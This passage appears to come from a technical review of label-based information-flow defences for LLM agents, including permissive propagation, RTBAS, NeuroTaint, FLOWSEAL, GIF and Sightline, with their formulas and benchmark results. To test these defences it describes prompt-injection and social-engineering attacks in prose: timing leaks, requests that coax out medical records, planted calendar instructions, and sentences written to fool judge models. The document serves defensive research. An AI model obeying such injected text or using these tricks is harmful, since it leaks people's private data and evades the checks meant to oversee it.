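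The survey *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) likewise finds that existing benchmarks rarely make an agent's next step depend on what it has just read, so they do not properly measure the harm from defences that block too much. *APPA* adds that AgentDojo tasks tend to end with the first action the agent takes after reading. A label that spreads too far therefore has no later step to block in these tasks, although there nearly always is one in a working day.

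The FIDES tests also have tidier labels than Alex's inbox would, because they counted only fields that an attack could reach as untrusted. Almost every message in Alex's inbox is private and comes from someone whose text the assistant should not obey. Once the assistant has read one email each from Marco and Priya, both FIDES conditions fail for every recipient except Alex. Variables help little if Alex asks the assistant to "deal with anything urgent", because the emails then determine the actions.

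It is also unclear which pieces of text need their own label. A colleague's email may quote a customer's message, which may quote someone else's. If the program trusts the whole email because the colleague sent it, the customer can give the assistant instructions. If it distrusts any email that contains outside text, much of the company's internal mail becomes untrusted. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists as an open challenge how to choose which parts of a prompt to label separately.

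Approvals would accumulate quickly under these conditions. Suppose an assistant drafts 60 replies a day, and 50 of them draw on a document the recipient was not sent. Each of those 50 needs a person's approval. After about 50 prompts, Anthropic's testers caught one in twenty dangerous commands. The testers saw their prompts in a single session, though, and an employee who gets 50 over a whole day may read them more carefully.

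## Removing the labels of inputs that had no influence: permissive propagation and RTBAS

An assistant would interrupt Alex less often if the label on each reply covered only the emails that the reply needed. To narrow the label this way, some component must identify the inputs that had no influence and remove their labels. That component usually also reads the attacker's text, so the security of each design depends on what an attacker can gain by misleading it.

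### Permissive propagation

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, proposed checking whether a smaller set of inputs would have served as well. Their program works as follows:

1. It runs the model on the full prompt, which gives a draft *y* and the usual strict label.
2. It looks for more permissive labels. For each one, it takes only the inputs that the label allows and measures how likely the model finds the draft *y* given those inputs alone. If the draft is almost as likely as before, the label passes, and the program tries still more permissive ones.
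3. It picks one of the most permissive labels that passed and runs the model again on only the inputs that this label allows.
4. It discards *y* and returns the new output with the new label.

The measure in step 2 is perplexity, which is low when the model finds a text likely. If the model gives the *n* tokens of the draft the probabilities *p*₁ to *p*ₙ, then

perplexity(*y*) = (*p*₁ · *p*₂ · … · *p*ₙ)^(−1/*n*).

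A label passes if the perplexity rises by at most a tolerance λ when the model sees only the inputs it allows.

Suppose Alex writes "Reply to Marco's email and say yes" when the prompt contains both Marco's email asking about Thursday and Priya's email with a sales preview. The model drafts "Yes, Thursday works." The draft's five tokens might have a perplexity of 1.2 with the full prompt and 1.25 without Priya's email, a rise of 0.05 that is within a tolerance of 0.2. If the program also removes Marco's email, nothing in the prompt indicates the day, and the probability of "Thursday" might fall from 0.9 to 0.05. That alone multiplies the perplexity by 18^(1/5), or about 1.8, so the test fails. The program therefore removes only Priya's email, regenerates the reply and labels it {Alex, Marco}. The reply can now go to Marco without approval.

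Testing labels takes much less computation than testing every subset of the inputs. If the only labels are "trusted" and "untrusted", one test is enough. If each of 14 documents has its own label, there are 2¹⁴ (16,384) possible combinations, although the search usually visits few of them. Siddiqui and colleagues prove that the search finds every best label if adding a document never makes the draft less likely. With real models, irrelevant text can make the draft less likely, so in practice the search is a heuristic.

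### Why the second run matters

The perplexity test can be wrong, and an attacker can plant text that distorts it. Even then, Priya's figures cannot appear in the reply, because the model wrote the final version in a fresh run that did not include her email. Siddiqui and colleagues point out that this protection holds even under prompt injection, because the program enforces it, not the model. The reply may be worse if it needed that email. The method resembles secure multi-execution, an older technique that runs a program once for each security level, using only the data allowed at that level.

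The program chooses the inputs after reading everything, so the choice can still leak a little information. Suppose Marco hides an instruction in his email to answer in French if the preview shows sales above 10 million. If sales are lower, the draft is in English, the test passes and Marco gets a reply at once. If they are higher, the draft is in French, which would be very unlikely without the preview, so the test fails and the reply waits for Alex's approval. Marco can learn one bit from whether the reply came straight away, and can send another email tomorrow with a different threshold.

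The participant rule, which gives the model only what the recipient may read, avoids this leak. Siddiqui and colleagues suggest a similar shortcut when the output's required label is known in advance. The search is more useful when nobody yet knows who will read the text, for example when a program saves an answer for reuse or an employee may later forward an email.

### Results with Llama 2

Siddiqui and colleagues built two versions of the test. One puts the documents in the prompt, as above. The other uses a nearest-neighbour language model, which mixes the predictions of a model that has not seen the documents with predictions looked up in them. This version needs only one extra model call, however many subsets the program tests. The baseline, introspection, prompts the model to list the documents that mattered.

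They used three datasets:

- **Personal records.** The 64 questions ask for the social security numbers and birth dates of invented people. Each question comes with 14 documents, and each document has its own label.
- **News.** The 3,465 questions concern pairs of reliable and unreliable articles on the same topic. For 647 of them, the label could be improved.
- **Agent conversations.** In 40 conversations, the assistant searches the web, email or a calendar. In 20 of them, the trusted results were enough to answer.

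| Dataset and measure | Method | Llama 2, 7B | Llama 2, 70B |
|---|---|---|---|
| Personal records: found exactly the right labels | Prompt | 85.9% | 85.9% |
| | Nearest neighbour | 53.1% | 57.8% |
| | Introspection | 1.6% | 12.7% |
| News: improved the label where possible | Prompt | 56.7% | 39.3% |
| Agent conversations: improved the label where possible | Prompt | 85% | 95% |
| | Introspection | 45% | 80% |

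The news figures assume a search step that always finds the relevant articles. With the smaller model, in about 23% of the cases where the program relaxed the label, it dropped an article that the answer needed. The second run kept these cases safe, but the new answer could differ from the original. In the agent conversations, the regenerated answers were slightly closer to the reference answers than the first drafts were, perhaps because the model had less irrelevant text.

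The results depend heavily on λ, and the best value differed between datasets. The experiments included no attacker. Siddiqui and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker could add distracting text to make the influence test fail, which would keep the strict label in place and block legitimate work. Costa and colleagues write that FIDES could use this method, but they left it out for simplicity.

### RTBAS: choosing what to hide before generation

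*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) applies the same idea to agents that call tools. Its Robust Tool-Based Agent System splits the conversation into regions, each with its own label. Before each model call, a screener marks the regions that the next step needs. The program joins the labels of the marked regions and hides every region whose label is stricter than the joined label. The model then chooses a tool call based on the remaining regions. If the joined label breaks the tool's policy, the program asks the user to confirm the call, regardless of how confident the screener was.

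Zhong and colleagues built two screeners. One is a second language model, which reads the conversation with numbered markers around each region and lists the relevant ones. The other uses attention. The agent writes a preliminary message, and a small open model then scores how strongly each earlier token *i* affected each token *o* of that message:

score(*i*, *o*) ≈ Σ |*A* · ∂*L*/∂*A*|,

where *A* is the attention weight between the two tokens, *L* is the model's loss on token *o* (high when the token surprises the model), and the sum runs over all of the model's attention weights for that pair. The score approximates how much the loss would change if token *i* were missing. A small neural network, trained on 40 AgentDojo cases, turns the scores into a yes or no for each region. It was right 81% of the time on test data.

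These scores come from a different model because GPT-4o, which writes the answer, does not have public internals. They are poor evidence of what influenced GPT-4o, but they are acceptable here because the program hides the regions. A wrong guess therefore leads to an unnecessary confirmation or a missing input.

An attacker can influence both screeners because they read the unredacted conversation. An injected line could persuade the judge model that a confidential file is essential, which would restore the file and its strict label, or that a useful file is irrelevant. In both cases, any text the model then sees keeps its label. But as with Marco's French reply, the attacker may learn something from whether a call runs immediately or waits for the user.

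RTBAS is weaker in two details. It treats regions without labels as trusted and public, whereas Siddiqui and colleagues suggest giving unlabelled documents the strictest label. In the published pseudocode, the model writes its final answer to the user from the full conversation, although the definitions call for the redacted one. This is probably a mistake, but code that followed the pseudocode would give some answers the wrong label.

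### What RTBAS achieved

On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policy. The program had no user to ask, so it skipped any call that needed confirmation. Without attacks, RTBAS completed 10% fewer tasks than an undefended agent when it used the judge screener, and 7.4% fewer when it used the attention screener. Under attack, the loss was less than 1% with the judge and about 3% with attention, because attacks also make the undefended agent fail tasks. The Slack tasks were affected most, with 22% completed with the judge and 33% with attention, because many of them ask the agent to act on text from untrusted websites.

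Zhong and colleagues also wrote 37 tasks involving payments, flights and shopping, in which the agent handles private details such as card numbers. They marked by hand which tool calls should need confirmation:

| Method | Asked needlessly | Failed to ask | Identified exactly which private data the call used |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hide all private data and never ask | 0% | 51.4% | 22.3% |
| Ask before every call | 29.7% | 0% | 56.7% |
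| RTBAS with judge | 8.1% | 10.8% | 70.0% |
| RTBAS with attention | 16.2% | 10.8% | 57.3% |

The failures to ask are not leaks, because the program had hidden the private data. In these cases, the agent usually could not finish the task properly. The attention screener identified the data each call used barely better than a method that assumes every call uses all the data. The judge did better, and Zhong and colleagues suspect that writing out its reasoning helped.

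On the banking tasks, RTBAS took about twice as long as an ordinary agent and cost about twice as much. It makes one screening call per step, however many labels there are, while Zhong and colleagues estimate that Siddiqui and colleagues' search would add 16 to 64 calls for a typical set of labels.

### Explaining an output after the model has written it

A system could also keep the original output and estimate which inputs influenced it. This avoids generating the answer a second time, but a wrong estimate can leak data. Suppose Priya's sales figures shaped the reply to Marco and the estimator misses this. If the program only drops the label on her email, the figures go to Marco, whereas if it hides the email and regenerates the reply, the reply may be incomplete.

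*Ghost in the Agent* describes a tool of this kind, NeuroTaint, which uses the estimates to audit finished runs rather than to relax labels. In the paper's example, an agent saves a confidential revenue forecast in its memory and uses it in a report days later, in a new session. NeuroTaint handles this by recording every tool call in a graph and storing each text's origin alongside it, so the text is still linked to its origin when the agent retrieves it.

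When the agent reaches a sink, NeuroTaint looks for traces of each earlier source in the call. It checks for:

- a unique marker that it had added to the source text
- a shared run of characters
- similar meaning, as measured by sentence embeddings (lists of numbers that represent what a text means)
- similar meaning to any one section of a long source

If NeuroTaint finds none of these, it gives a judge model the original history and a copy in which a neutral placeholder, such as "No relevant information found.", replaces the source. The judge predicts whether the agent would still have made the same call with the copy. If the judge predicts that it would not, NeuroTaint reports that the source influenced the decision.

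The test set, TaintBench, has 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks, and in 200 of the scenarios a source influences the sink. NeuroTaint found 187 of these 200 real flows and raised 16 false alarms. It found 37 of the 40 flows where the source only affected a decision, and 28 of the 30 that crossed sessions or agents. Fourteen of the false alarms came from scenarios where the output only shared a topic with the source, and NeuroTaint flagged every scenario of that type.

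A version of FIDES found 108 flows, missed 92 and raised 106 false alarms. This comparison is probably unfair to FIDES, because the conservative rule should not miss a flow from a labelled source within a single run. The FIDES version flagged nothing in four frameworks, which accounts for 40 of the misses and suggests that the setup did not fit those frameworks.

An audit is useful for finding leaks afterwards, and it added only about a quarter of a second per run. Using NeuroTaint to remove labels would be riskier. It would have dropped the label in 13 of the 200 real flows (6.5%), before anyone had tried to evade it. An attacker could cause this deliberately, because the judge reads the attacker's text and NeuroTaint replaces sources one at a time. If two emails contain the same instruction, the agent would still obey one when the other is replaced, so the judge could correctly conclude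 each time that the agent would still have made the call, and clear both emails. This works only if the call contains no recognisable text from either email, which is the case the judge is meant to handle.

Two later designs try to make the estimates more reliable. Geometric Information Flow measures influence through the model's gradients, and Sightline, by Xu and colleagues, removes labels at a chosen error rate.

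### FLOWSEAL: a separate model at the exit

Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) argue in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* that a model should not decide whether a privacy rule applies when an attacker controls part of its input. An attacker who stops the model from recognising a request as sensitive bypasses every check that would have followed.

They showed this with a defence in which the agent's instructions told it to verify the identity of anyone requesting information and wait for the data owner's consent. In their running example, Jane's agent holds the medical records of a man named Mark, and his ex-wife Emily wants them. Three kinds of request worked without any prompt injection:

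- Emily shares a page of "professional notes" and asks Jane to fill in her section. The agent treats this as teamwork.
- Emily shares a list of true and invented facts about Mark and asks Jane to delete the wrong ones. The entries that remain are the true ones.
- Emily asks by email for the single word "completed", while a shared page asks for the details. The agent does not connect the two.

Their own system, FLOWSEAL, uses ordinary code to decide when to check outgoing text. Someone first registers the sensitive records, their owner and who may receive them. The code then intercepts every tool call that writes or shares something. It lets messages to trusted recipients through and always blocks those to blacklisted ones. For an unknown recipient, it sends a separate model the protected records and the exact text the agent wants to send. This model does not see the conversation and may answer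 only "SAFE" or "BLOCKED". After a block, the agent can rewrite the text or request the owner's consent.

| Attack | Items leaked, instructions only | Items leaked, FLOWSEAL |
|---|---|---|
| Earlier attack that fakes the owner's consent | 1.9% | 0% |
| Shared notes | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Deleting wrong entries | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Two channels | 43.8% | 2.2% |

FLOWSEAL completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, compared with 44.7% with the instructions. A simpler set of instructions reached 75.9% but leaked 13% to 55% of items under the new attacks. FLOWSEAL also delivered fewer records when sharing was appropriate. In a test where the owner would agree if asked, it delivered 32.7% of the records, compared with 61% to 86% for the other defences, mainly because the agent asked for consent less often.

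Shim and colleagues also removed parts of the system to measure what each contributed. Without the interception code, the shared-notes attack leaked 28.4% of items. With the code set to block everything to unknown recipients, 1.3% leaked, but the agent completed no ordinary tasks. With the code set to allow everything, 24.9% leaked. So the code ensures that a check takes place, but FLOWSEAL's usefulness depends on the checking model, which in effect removes the label from each message it classifies as safe.

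Their theorem has the same dependence. It guarantees that nothing derived from a protected record reaches an unauthorised recipient unless the checker wrongly answers "SAFE", but it does not bound how often that happens. Shim and colleagues also wrongly assert that FIDES leaves all enforcement to the model, when FIDES checks its labels in code.

### What can reach the checker

Emily cannot talk to the checker directly, and her story about teamwork never reaches it, which is an improvement over a single model that reads everything. But the checker reads the proposed text, and the agent writes that text at her request. She can ask the agent for a paraphrase, a coded version or a sentence addressed to the checker. Shim and colleagues name paraphrase as the checker's main weakness and concede that an attacker might split one fact across several harmless-looking messages. If a protected record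 is an email from a stranger, the checker also reads the stranger's words directly.

The results provide little evidence about attacks of this kind. Shim and colleagues exclude prompt injection, partly on the grounds that newer models resist it better. They also tested FLOWSEAL on real Gmail and Notion accounts, where the deletion attack leaked 34.7% of items past a defence called PrivacyChecker and none past FLOWSEAL. That test counted a leak only if a sensitive fact appeared word for word, so it could not detect paraphrases.

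The rewriting step creates another chance for a leak. After a block, the agent tries again with the records still in its context, so preventing a leak in the new version depends on the checker as much as it did in the old one. If the program instead generated the rewrite in a fresh call without the records, as permissive propagation does, Mark's diagnosis could not appear in it, regardless of Emily's request or the checker's answer.

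## Geometric Information Flow: measuring influence through the model's gradients

The RTBAS judge and NeuroTaint both rely on a language model to judge which inputs mattered, and an attacker's text can sway that judgment. Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026) at Columbia University developed Geometric Information Flow (GIF), which calculates influence from the model's gradients, which describe how its output would change if its input changed slightly. GIF gives an amount of information in bits for each passage of the prompt, rather than a yes-or-no label. This stage doesn't rely on a language model's judgment, though an attacker can still change the amount by choosing different words.

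### Noise in one passage

A language model first converts each token of the prompt into an embedding, a list of up to several thousand numbers. We can add a little random noise to the embeddings of a single passage, such as Priya's sales preview, and leave the rest of the prompt unchanged. If the next-token probabilities then change a lot, the model is sensitive to that passage.

GIF defines the flow from the passage as the mutual information between the noise and the next token, which is how much learning one reduces the uncertainty about the other. Aarhus University's lecture slides *Quantitative security* (2025) state that the initial uncertainty equals the information leaked plus the remaining uncertainty. For example, if a program prints the last 5 bits of a random 32-bit number, an observer's uncertainty falls from 32 bits to 27, so the mutual information is 5 bits.

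Write *U* for the noise, which is Gaussian (bell-shaped) with variance τ in every coordinate, and *Y* for the next token. Then

I(*U*; *Y*) = H(average prediction) − average of H(prediction),

where H is entropy, the uncertainty of a probability distribution in bits. If the noise never changes the prediction, the two terms are equal and the flow is zero.

Nobody can calculate this exactly for a real model, because that would require averaging the model's predictions over every possible value of the noise. GIF replaces the model with a simpler system that behaves almost identically when the noise is small.

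### From derivatives to bits

The replacement uses two standard quantities:

- **The Jacobian, *J*,** is a table of derivatives. Each entry gives the rate at which one number in the model's final internal state changes as one number in the passage's embeddings changes.
- **The Fisher information, *F*,** describes how much the prediction changes when the scores behind it change. A small change matters a lot when two candidate tokens are close and very little when one of them already has a probability of 99.9%. For next-token probabilities *p*, it is *F* = diag(*p*) − *pp*ᵀ.

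A third table, *W*, belongs to the model and turns its final internal state into a score for each token. Multiplying the three gives *A* = *F*^½ *WJ*, which converts noise in the passage into movement of the prediction. GIF then treats the model as a Gaussian channel, the textbook model of a noisy line. The signal *U* goes in, and *AU* comes out with standard Gaussian noise added. The information that passes through such a channel has a known formula:

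GIF = ½ log₂ det(*I* + τ*AA*ᵀ) = ½ Σ log₂(1 + τλᵢ),

where *I* is the identity matrix and the λᵢ are the eigenvalues of *AA*ᵀ. Each eigenvalue measures how strongly the prediction responds to noise in one direction. Directions that the model ignores have an eigenvalue of zero and add nothing to the sum.

When τ is small, the result is close to τ/2 times the sum of the eigenvalues, in nats. Štorek and colleagues call that sum the influence. It takes less computation than the channel formula, and the approximation is never below the formula's value. The influences of separate passages add up, so an email's influence is the total over its tokens.

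*Jacobian Scopes* (Liu, Zadeoğlu et al., 2026) used the same ingredients a few months earlier to explain predictions. One of its methods keeps only the direction in which the prediction is most sensitive, so it needs only one backward pass through the model. When a small Llama model translated Dante's *Inferno*, this method traced the predicted word "world" to the Italian "mondo". For a phrase with no literal equivalent, it traced the prediction to several words of the original. GIF adds an interpretation in bits and a proof of what those bits bound.

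### A prompt made of one number

Suppose the prompt is a single number *x*, and the model can answer only "yes" or "no". The score for "yes" is *z* = 2*x*, the score for "no" is 0, and the probability of "yes" is 1/(1 + e^(−*z*)). At *x* = 0 the two answers are equally likely.

1. The Jacobian is 2, because *z* changes by 2 for each unit change in *x*.
2. The Fisher information for a choice between two answers is *p*(1 − *p*), which is 0.25 here.
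3. The single eigenvalue is 2² × 0.25 = 1.
4. With τ = 0.1, the channel formula gives ½ log₂(1 + 0.1 × 1) ≈ 0.069 bits.

Noise of this size keeps the probability of "yes" between about 35% and 65% two thirds of the time. Integrating numerically over the noise gives an actual mutual information of about 0.063 bits. The formula overestimates this slightly, which is the safer way to be wrong. The simpler approximation from the influence gives 0.072 bits.

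With τ = 100, however, the formula gives 3.3 bits, although a yes/no answer can carry at most one. The approximation holds only for small noise. For larger noise, the estimate keeps growing but no longer corresponds to anything the model could do.

### A hiring assistant and 82 bits

In one example from Štorek and colleagues, a hiring assistant reads a CV containing injected text. GIF assigns 82 bits to the injected text, 27 to the system prompt (the developer's instructions) and 16 to everything else. The injected text accounts for about two thirds of the total, which is a good reason to stop and check before the assistant acts.

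The 82-bit figure does not mean that the output contains 82 bits of secret data or that an attacker could extract that many. It would change with the noise level τ. A token chosen from a vocabulary of 100,000 carries at most log₂ 100,000, or about 16.6 bits, so the figure must either cover several output tokens or overestimate the flow. Even an accurate figure would be a Shannon average, which can understate a dangerous leak. GIF's bits are therefore a poor basis for a leak budget that counts possible answers.

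A high score also does not show that anything is wrong. A hiring assistant is supposed to be influenced by CVs, so an honest applicant's impressive CV should score highly too. GIF measures how much influence a passage has, so a separate check has to decide whether that influence is allowed.

The measure can still reveal attacks that a check of the outcome misses. In one AgentDojo test, text planted in a calendar event told an agent running on Qwen 3 14B to send the body of someone's email to an outside address. The agent emailed the event's details to that address instead. AgentDojo counted the attack as a failure because the agent sent the wrong text. GIF traced 31% of the information in the recipient's address to the injected instruction, while RTBAS's attention scores pointed mainly to harmless text.

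### What the Lean proof covers

The central theorem, which Lean has checked, is called local soundness:

I(*U*; *Y*) ≤ GIF(τ) + o(τ) as τ → 0.

The term o(τ) stands for an error that becomes negligible compared with τ as the noise shrinks. The theorem therefore rules out a measure that reports almost nothing while small changes to a passage noticeably steer the output. The proof has three steps:

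1. It replaces the average prediction, which nobody can compute, with the model's prediction for the actual prompt. This can only increase the estimated flow.
2. It shows that the average distance between the noisy predictions and the actual one is τ/2 times the influence, plus o(τ). The distance here is the Kullback–Leibler divergence, a standard measure of how far apart two probability distributions are.
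3. It replaces the influence with the channel formula. The two differ by at most (τ²/4) times the square of the influence, which o(τ) absorbs.

The second step assumes that, close to the actual prompt, the error in the Jacobian's linear estimate is at most a constant times the square of the noise. The proof does not show that any particular deployed model meets this condition, although models built from smooth functions should. It also does not give the size of the error for a particular τ.

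The bigger gap is that the theorem covers only small noise in the embeddings, and actual changes to a text are larger. Changing "Thursday" to "Friday" replaces one embedding with another, and swapping a harmless paragraph for an injected instruction replaces hundreds. A score near zero therefore does not prove that the output would have been the same without the passage. Xu and colleagues prove that the score also shrinks when the model is nearly certain of its answer, even if the passage determined that answer.

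This affects how to read another example from Štorek and colleagues. An agent turned private notes into a public Reddit comment that named a neighbour but left out the neighbour's home address, so the correct flow for the address is zero. GIF gave it zero, and an attention measure gave it 9%. But Štorek and colleagues describe GIF's result as certifying zero flow, which is more than the theorem supports. A guarantee would require a program to regenerate the comment without the address, as permissive propagation does.

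The theorem also applies only to a single next token, but a tool call contains many. A company would need its own rule for adding up or comparing scores across tokens.

### Making the calculation affordable

An exact calculation needs one backward pass through the model for every number in its internal state. That is 2,880 passes per output token for GPT OSS 120B, an open model from OpenAI, and 5,376 for Google's Gemma 4 31B.

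Štorek and colleagues avoid this by estimating only the influence. If *M* = *A*ᵀ*A* and *z* is a list of independent standard Gaussian random numbers, the average of *z*ᵀ*Mz* over many draws approximates the sum of *M*'s eigenvalues. Each draw needs one forward and one backward derivative pass through the network, with a little arithmetic between them. A published algorithm, Hutch++, reduces the number of draws needed.

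They compared the estimate with the exact calculation on 150 tokens from AgentDojo tool calls, using a very small model, Qwen 3 0.6B:

| Rank of the approximation | Agreement with the exact ranking (Spearman correlation) | Relative error in the amounts |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.957 | 63% |
| 8 | 0.986 | 41% |
| 64 | 0.988 | 36% |

So an estimate that uses little compute ranks the tokens in nearly the right order but gets the amounts wrong by a third or more. Hutch++ is guaranteed to estimate the amounts to within 10% of the true influence, with 95% probability, if it uses 181 products with *M*. Nobody has yet proved this guarantee in Lean, so the Lean development assumes it and checks only what follows from it.

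### Ranking tokens on three benchmarks

The evaluation ran agents on six open models: Qwen 3 (8B, 14B and 32B), Gemma 4 31B, and GPT OSS (20B and 120B). AgentDojo and MSB, a benchmark of attacks through MCP tools, tested whether an injection took control of an action. AgentDAM tested whether an agent revealed private information while using simulated GitLab, Reddit and shopping sites.

For each tool call an agent made, GIF ranked the earlier tokens by their influence on the call. Štorek and colleagues then calculated what share of the top *k* tokens belonged to the injected instruction or, in AgentDAM, to the private information. A run's score was the highest share across all its calls.

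A company could refuse any run whose score exceeds a threshold. The evaluation does not choose one, because the different methods' scores are not comparable. It reports two measures that cover every possible threshold. AUROC is the probability that a run with a violation scores higher than a run without one, and 50% is what chance would give. AUPRC is roughly the share of flagged runs that were real violations, averaged over every level of strictness. The table gives both for *k* = 50, averaged over the six models:

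| Benchmark | GIF | Simple gradient | RTBAS attention |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 91% / 70% | 90% / 69% | 84% / 58% |
| MSB | 92% / 93% | 92% / 94% | 76% / 82% |
| AgentDAM | 75% / 44% | 74% / 38% | 57% / 31% |

The simple gradient measures only the effect on the score of the token the model chose and ignores the rest of the distribution, but it does almost as well as GIF on the two injection benchmarks. The benefit over attention therefore comes mainly from using gradients, and the additional geometry matters more for the theorem than for these results. The ranking also depends on the model, since attention beat GIF on AgentDojo with Gemma 4 31B, with an AUROC of 94% against 80%.

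GIF's AUROC also depends on *k*, the number of top tokens it examines. Averaged over models and benchmarks, AUROC rose from 66% at *k* = 1 to 87% at *k* = 50, with most of the gain coming by about *k* = 30.

Štorek and colleagues also asked GPT-5.5, at its highest reasoning setting, to pick out the influential tokens in a sample of the runs. Averaged over the values of *k*, GIF's AUROC was 11% higher and its AUPRC 12% higher. GIF cost $15.98, compared with $147.90 for GPT-5.5. The performance gap narrowed as *k* grew, and at *k* = 50 the AUROC was 91% for GIF and 87% for GPT-5.5.

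These tests measure a signal, not a working defence, because the score depends on the benchmark's labels for which words are the injection. In Alex's inbox, a program would know that Marco's whole email is untrusted but not which sentence is hostile. An honest question from Marco should also strongly influence the reply, so a threshold on all untrusted text would flag ordinary correspondence.

### False alarms without a judge

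The group's summary reports that GIF, without any further check, caught almost every violation (near-perfect recall). Any detector can do this by flagging nearly everything, so the important figure is the number of false alarms.

GIF's AUPRC on AgentDAM was 44%, so on average more than half of the runs it flagged were false alarms. Attention reached 31%, little better than chance, so GIF's scores were an improvement but still produced many unnecessary warnings. Injection attacks were easier to separate from normal behaviour, particularly in MSB.

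In a stricter test, Xu and colleagues set each method's threshold so that it missed about 1% of the real flows in calls from open-source programs, then measured the share of spurious flows it removed. Their stronger version of GIF, which adds up the scores over the first 32 output tokens, removed 0.6–12.1% of the spurious flows, depending on the model. Setting the threshold on a different collection of programs raised this range to 3.1–22.1%.

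The two groups' results also differ on AgentDojo with Qwen 3 8B. Štorek and colleagues measured an AUROC of 76% to 93% for GIF, depending on *k*. Xu and colleagues found that none of the seven existing methods they tested, including GIF, exceeded 73.6% at detecting calls that carried out an attack. They scored the flow from the whole injected block instead of counting injected tokens near the top of a ranking, and they turned off the model's reasoning mode, which the GIF evaluation left on. They also wrote their own version of GIF and were comparing it with a competing tool, which may have hurt its results. Still, the gap suggests that GIF's performance depends considerably on how a system turns its scores into a decision.

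GIF is also slow for something that would run on every call. In the same tests, it took 7 to 14 times as long as a method that needs only one forward pass.

### Adding a lightweight judge

To reduce the false alarms, Štorek and colleagues add a language model that judges whether the influence was legitimate. For each tool call, GIF picks the one to three most influential passages among those the security policy covers. The judge receives these passages, highlighted, along with the user's task and the proposed action, and answers "allow" or "deny". If it denies any action, the whole run counts as a violation.

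They compared this with giving the same judge the entire record of the run. The judges were Qwen 3 8B, GPT OSS 120B, Gemma 4 31B and GPT-5.5. Across all judges and measures, scores with the short version were between 0.97 and 1.22 times those with the full record. The weakest judge, Qwen 3 8B, improved most, by 9% to 12% in F1 (a combined measure of false alarms and missed violations). On AgentDojo and MSB, Qwen 3 8B with three passages from GIF matched GPT-5.5 with the full record, at less than 1/81 of the cost.

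Most of that saving comes from replacing an expensive model with a small one. Selecting passages reduced the token count by a factor of at most 3.7 on the two injection benchmarks. On AgentDAM, the judge still used 76% to 81% of the tokens, because those agents keep little history and most of the text is in a few long web pages.

Injected text can fool the judge, a weakness that the gradient calculation had avoided. In a successful attack, the most influential passage is probably the attacker's own text, so GIF puts that text in front of the judge. The attacks in AgentDojo and MSB target the agent, but a determined attacker would also add a sentence for the judge, such as a claim that the user had approved the transfer. A shorter record also gives the judge less material for checking such a claim. A company could limit the damage by letting the judge block calls but not remove labels, so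 that the ordinary label check still applies when the judge is fooled.

### Small models in place of closed ones

Computing gradients requires access to a model's weights, which companies that use GPT or Claude do not have. Štorek and colleagues therefore tested whether a small open model could stand in for the one that produced the output. They computed GIF on Qwen 3 0.6B, using AgentDojo runs from Qwen 3 32B and from GPT OSS 120B, which is 200 times larger than the small model and comes from a different developer.

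Replacing the original model with the small one changed F1 by at most 0.7 percentage points and every other measure by at most 0.9. Using the small model also greatly reduces the compute GIF needs for open models, since the gradients can come from a network that fits on an ordinary graphics card.

Because the comparison kept the judge, it shows that the small model usually picked passages that led to the same verdict, but not that the two models' scores in bits agree. Both large models were open, and the runs came from a single benchmark whose injections tend to be conspicuous blocks of text. A small model might have more trouble tracing a business secret that subtly changes a recommendation, particularly if it could not have worked out the recommendation itself.

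The proof does not transfer between models either. When the gradients come from Qwen 3 0.6B, local soundness bounds how much a passage could affect that model's next token. The model that wrote Alex's email may have used Priya's figures in a way that Qwen 3 0.6B would not, and the theorem does not bound that difference.

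## Sightline: pruning labels at a chosen error rate

GIF's scores shrink when a model is nearly certain of its answer, as it often is when it picks a recipient or answers yes or no. Sightline, built by Xu and colleagues, uses the model's attention instead. After a model call, Sightline decides whether each input reached the output, and the program can then drop the labels of the inputs that did not, a step called pruning. The program keeps the original output, so a wrongly dropped label can let data out. Sightline therefore lets its operator set a limit on such misses, for example 1% of the inputs that did reach an output.

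### What counts as reaching the output

An input reaches the output if the output visibly reflects the input's content. This includes copying, translating or summarising the content, or using it to determine a decision, a number, the format or the length. An input does not reach the output if the model ignores it, lacks the information or ability to use it, or refuses the request. If Sightline keeps the label of such an input, the result is a spurious flow.

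In the paper's running example, a program inserts a query and a delimiter (a marker that separates parts of a prompt), and the model answers with a short decision. The answer depends on the query but not on the delimiter, so the query's label should stay and the delimiter's can be removed.

The definition comes from an earlier study by some of the same researchers, *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (Xu, Cheng and colleagues, 2026). It sorted 8,119 input-output pairs into 25 kinds of relation, from word-for-word copying to no visible effect.

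This is a looser standard than noninterference. If a confidential document makes the model refuse a request it would otherwise have carried out, the refusal reveals something about the document, but the document doesn't count as having reached the output. The word "visibly" also matters, because language models assigned the labels by reading the prompt and the output. The meeting date that revealed Project X's revenue to Bob meets the definition, since the revenue determined the date, but a judge could easily overlook it.

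### Influence travels along attention

A transformer keeps a list of numbers, the state, for each token and updates it layer by layer. Most operations work on each position separately, and only attention moves information from one position to another. Each layer has several attention heads. At position *t*, a head gives every position *i* up to *t* a weight *a*ₜᵢ, with the weights adding up to 1, and computes the weighted sum

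*o*ₜ = Σ *a*ₜᵢ *v*ᵢ,

where *v*ᵢ is a value computed from the state at position *i*.

A small change at an earlier position *s* can affect this sum in two ways. It can change the value *v*ₛ, or it can change the weights themselves. Xu and colleagues differentiate the sum and find that both effects contain the factor *a*ₜₛ:

‖∂*o*ₜ/∂*h*ₛ‖ ≤ *a*ₜₛ · *c*ₜₛ,

where *h*ₛ is the state at position *s* and *c*ₜₛ depends on the head's parameters and the current states. A head that gives position *s* no weight therefore passes on no small change from it.

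The result also extends through all the layers. To first order (for very small changes), an input can affect the output only through a chain of attention weights connecting them. GIF's measure of flow uses the same derivatives, so the bound applies to it too. The proof has been checked in Lean.

The theorem does not cover some current hybrid models, which replace most attention layers with state-space layers that carry forward a running summary of the text. An input can erase earlier information from that summary even if no attention head gives the input any weight.

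In practice the theorem rules out very little, because attention weights are almost never exactly zero. Pruning therefore requires judging whether a given amount of attention matters, and Xu and colleagues prove three results about how such judgments go wrong.

### How the evidence can mislead

First, a model can attend to a passage without using it. An attention head can put nearly all its weight on a passage and add nothing to the model's state, or a second head can cancel what the first one added. Xu and colleagues construct a case in which every head attends to one passage at least as much as to another, but only the less-attended passage changes the output. A score that always rises with attention would rank these two passages in the wrong order.

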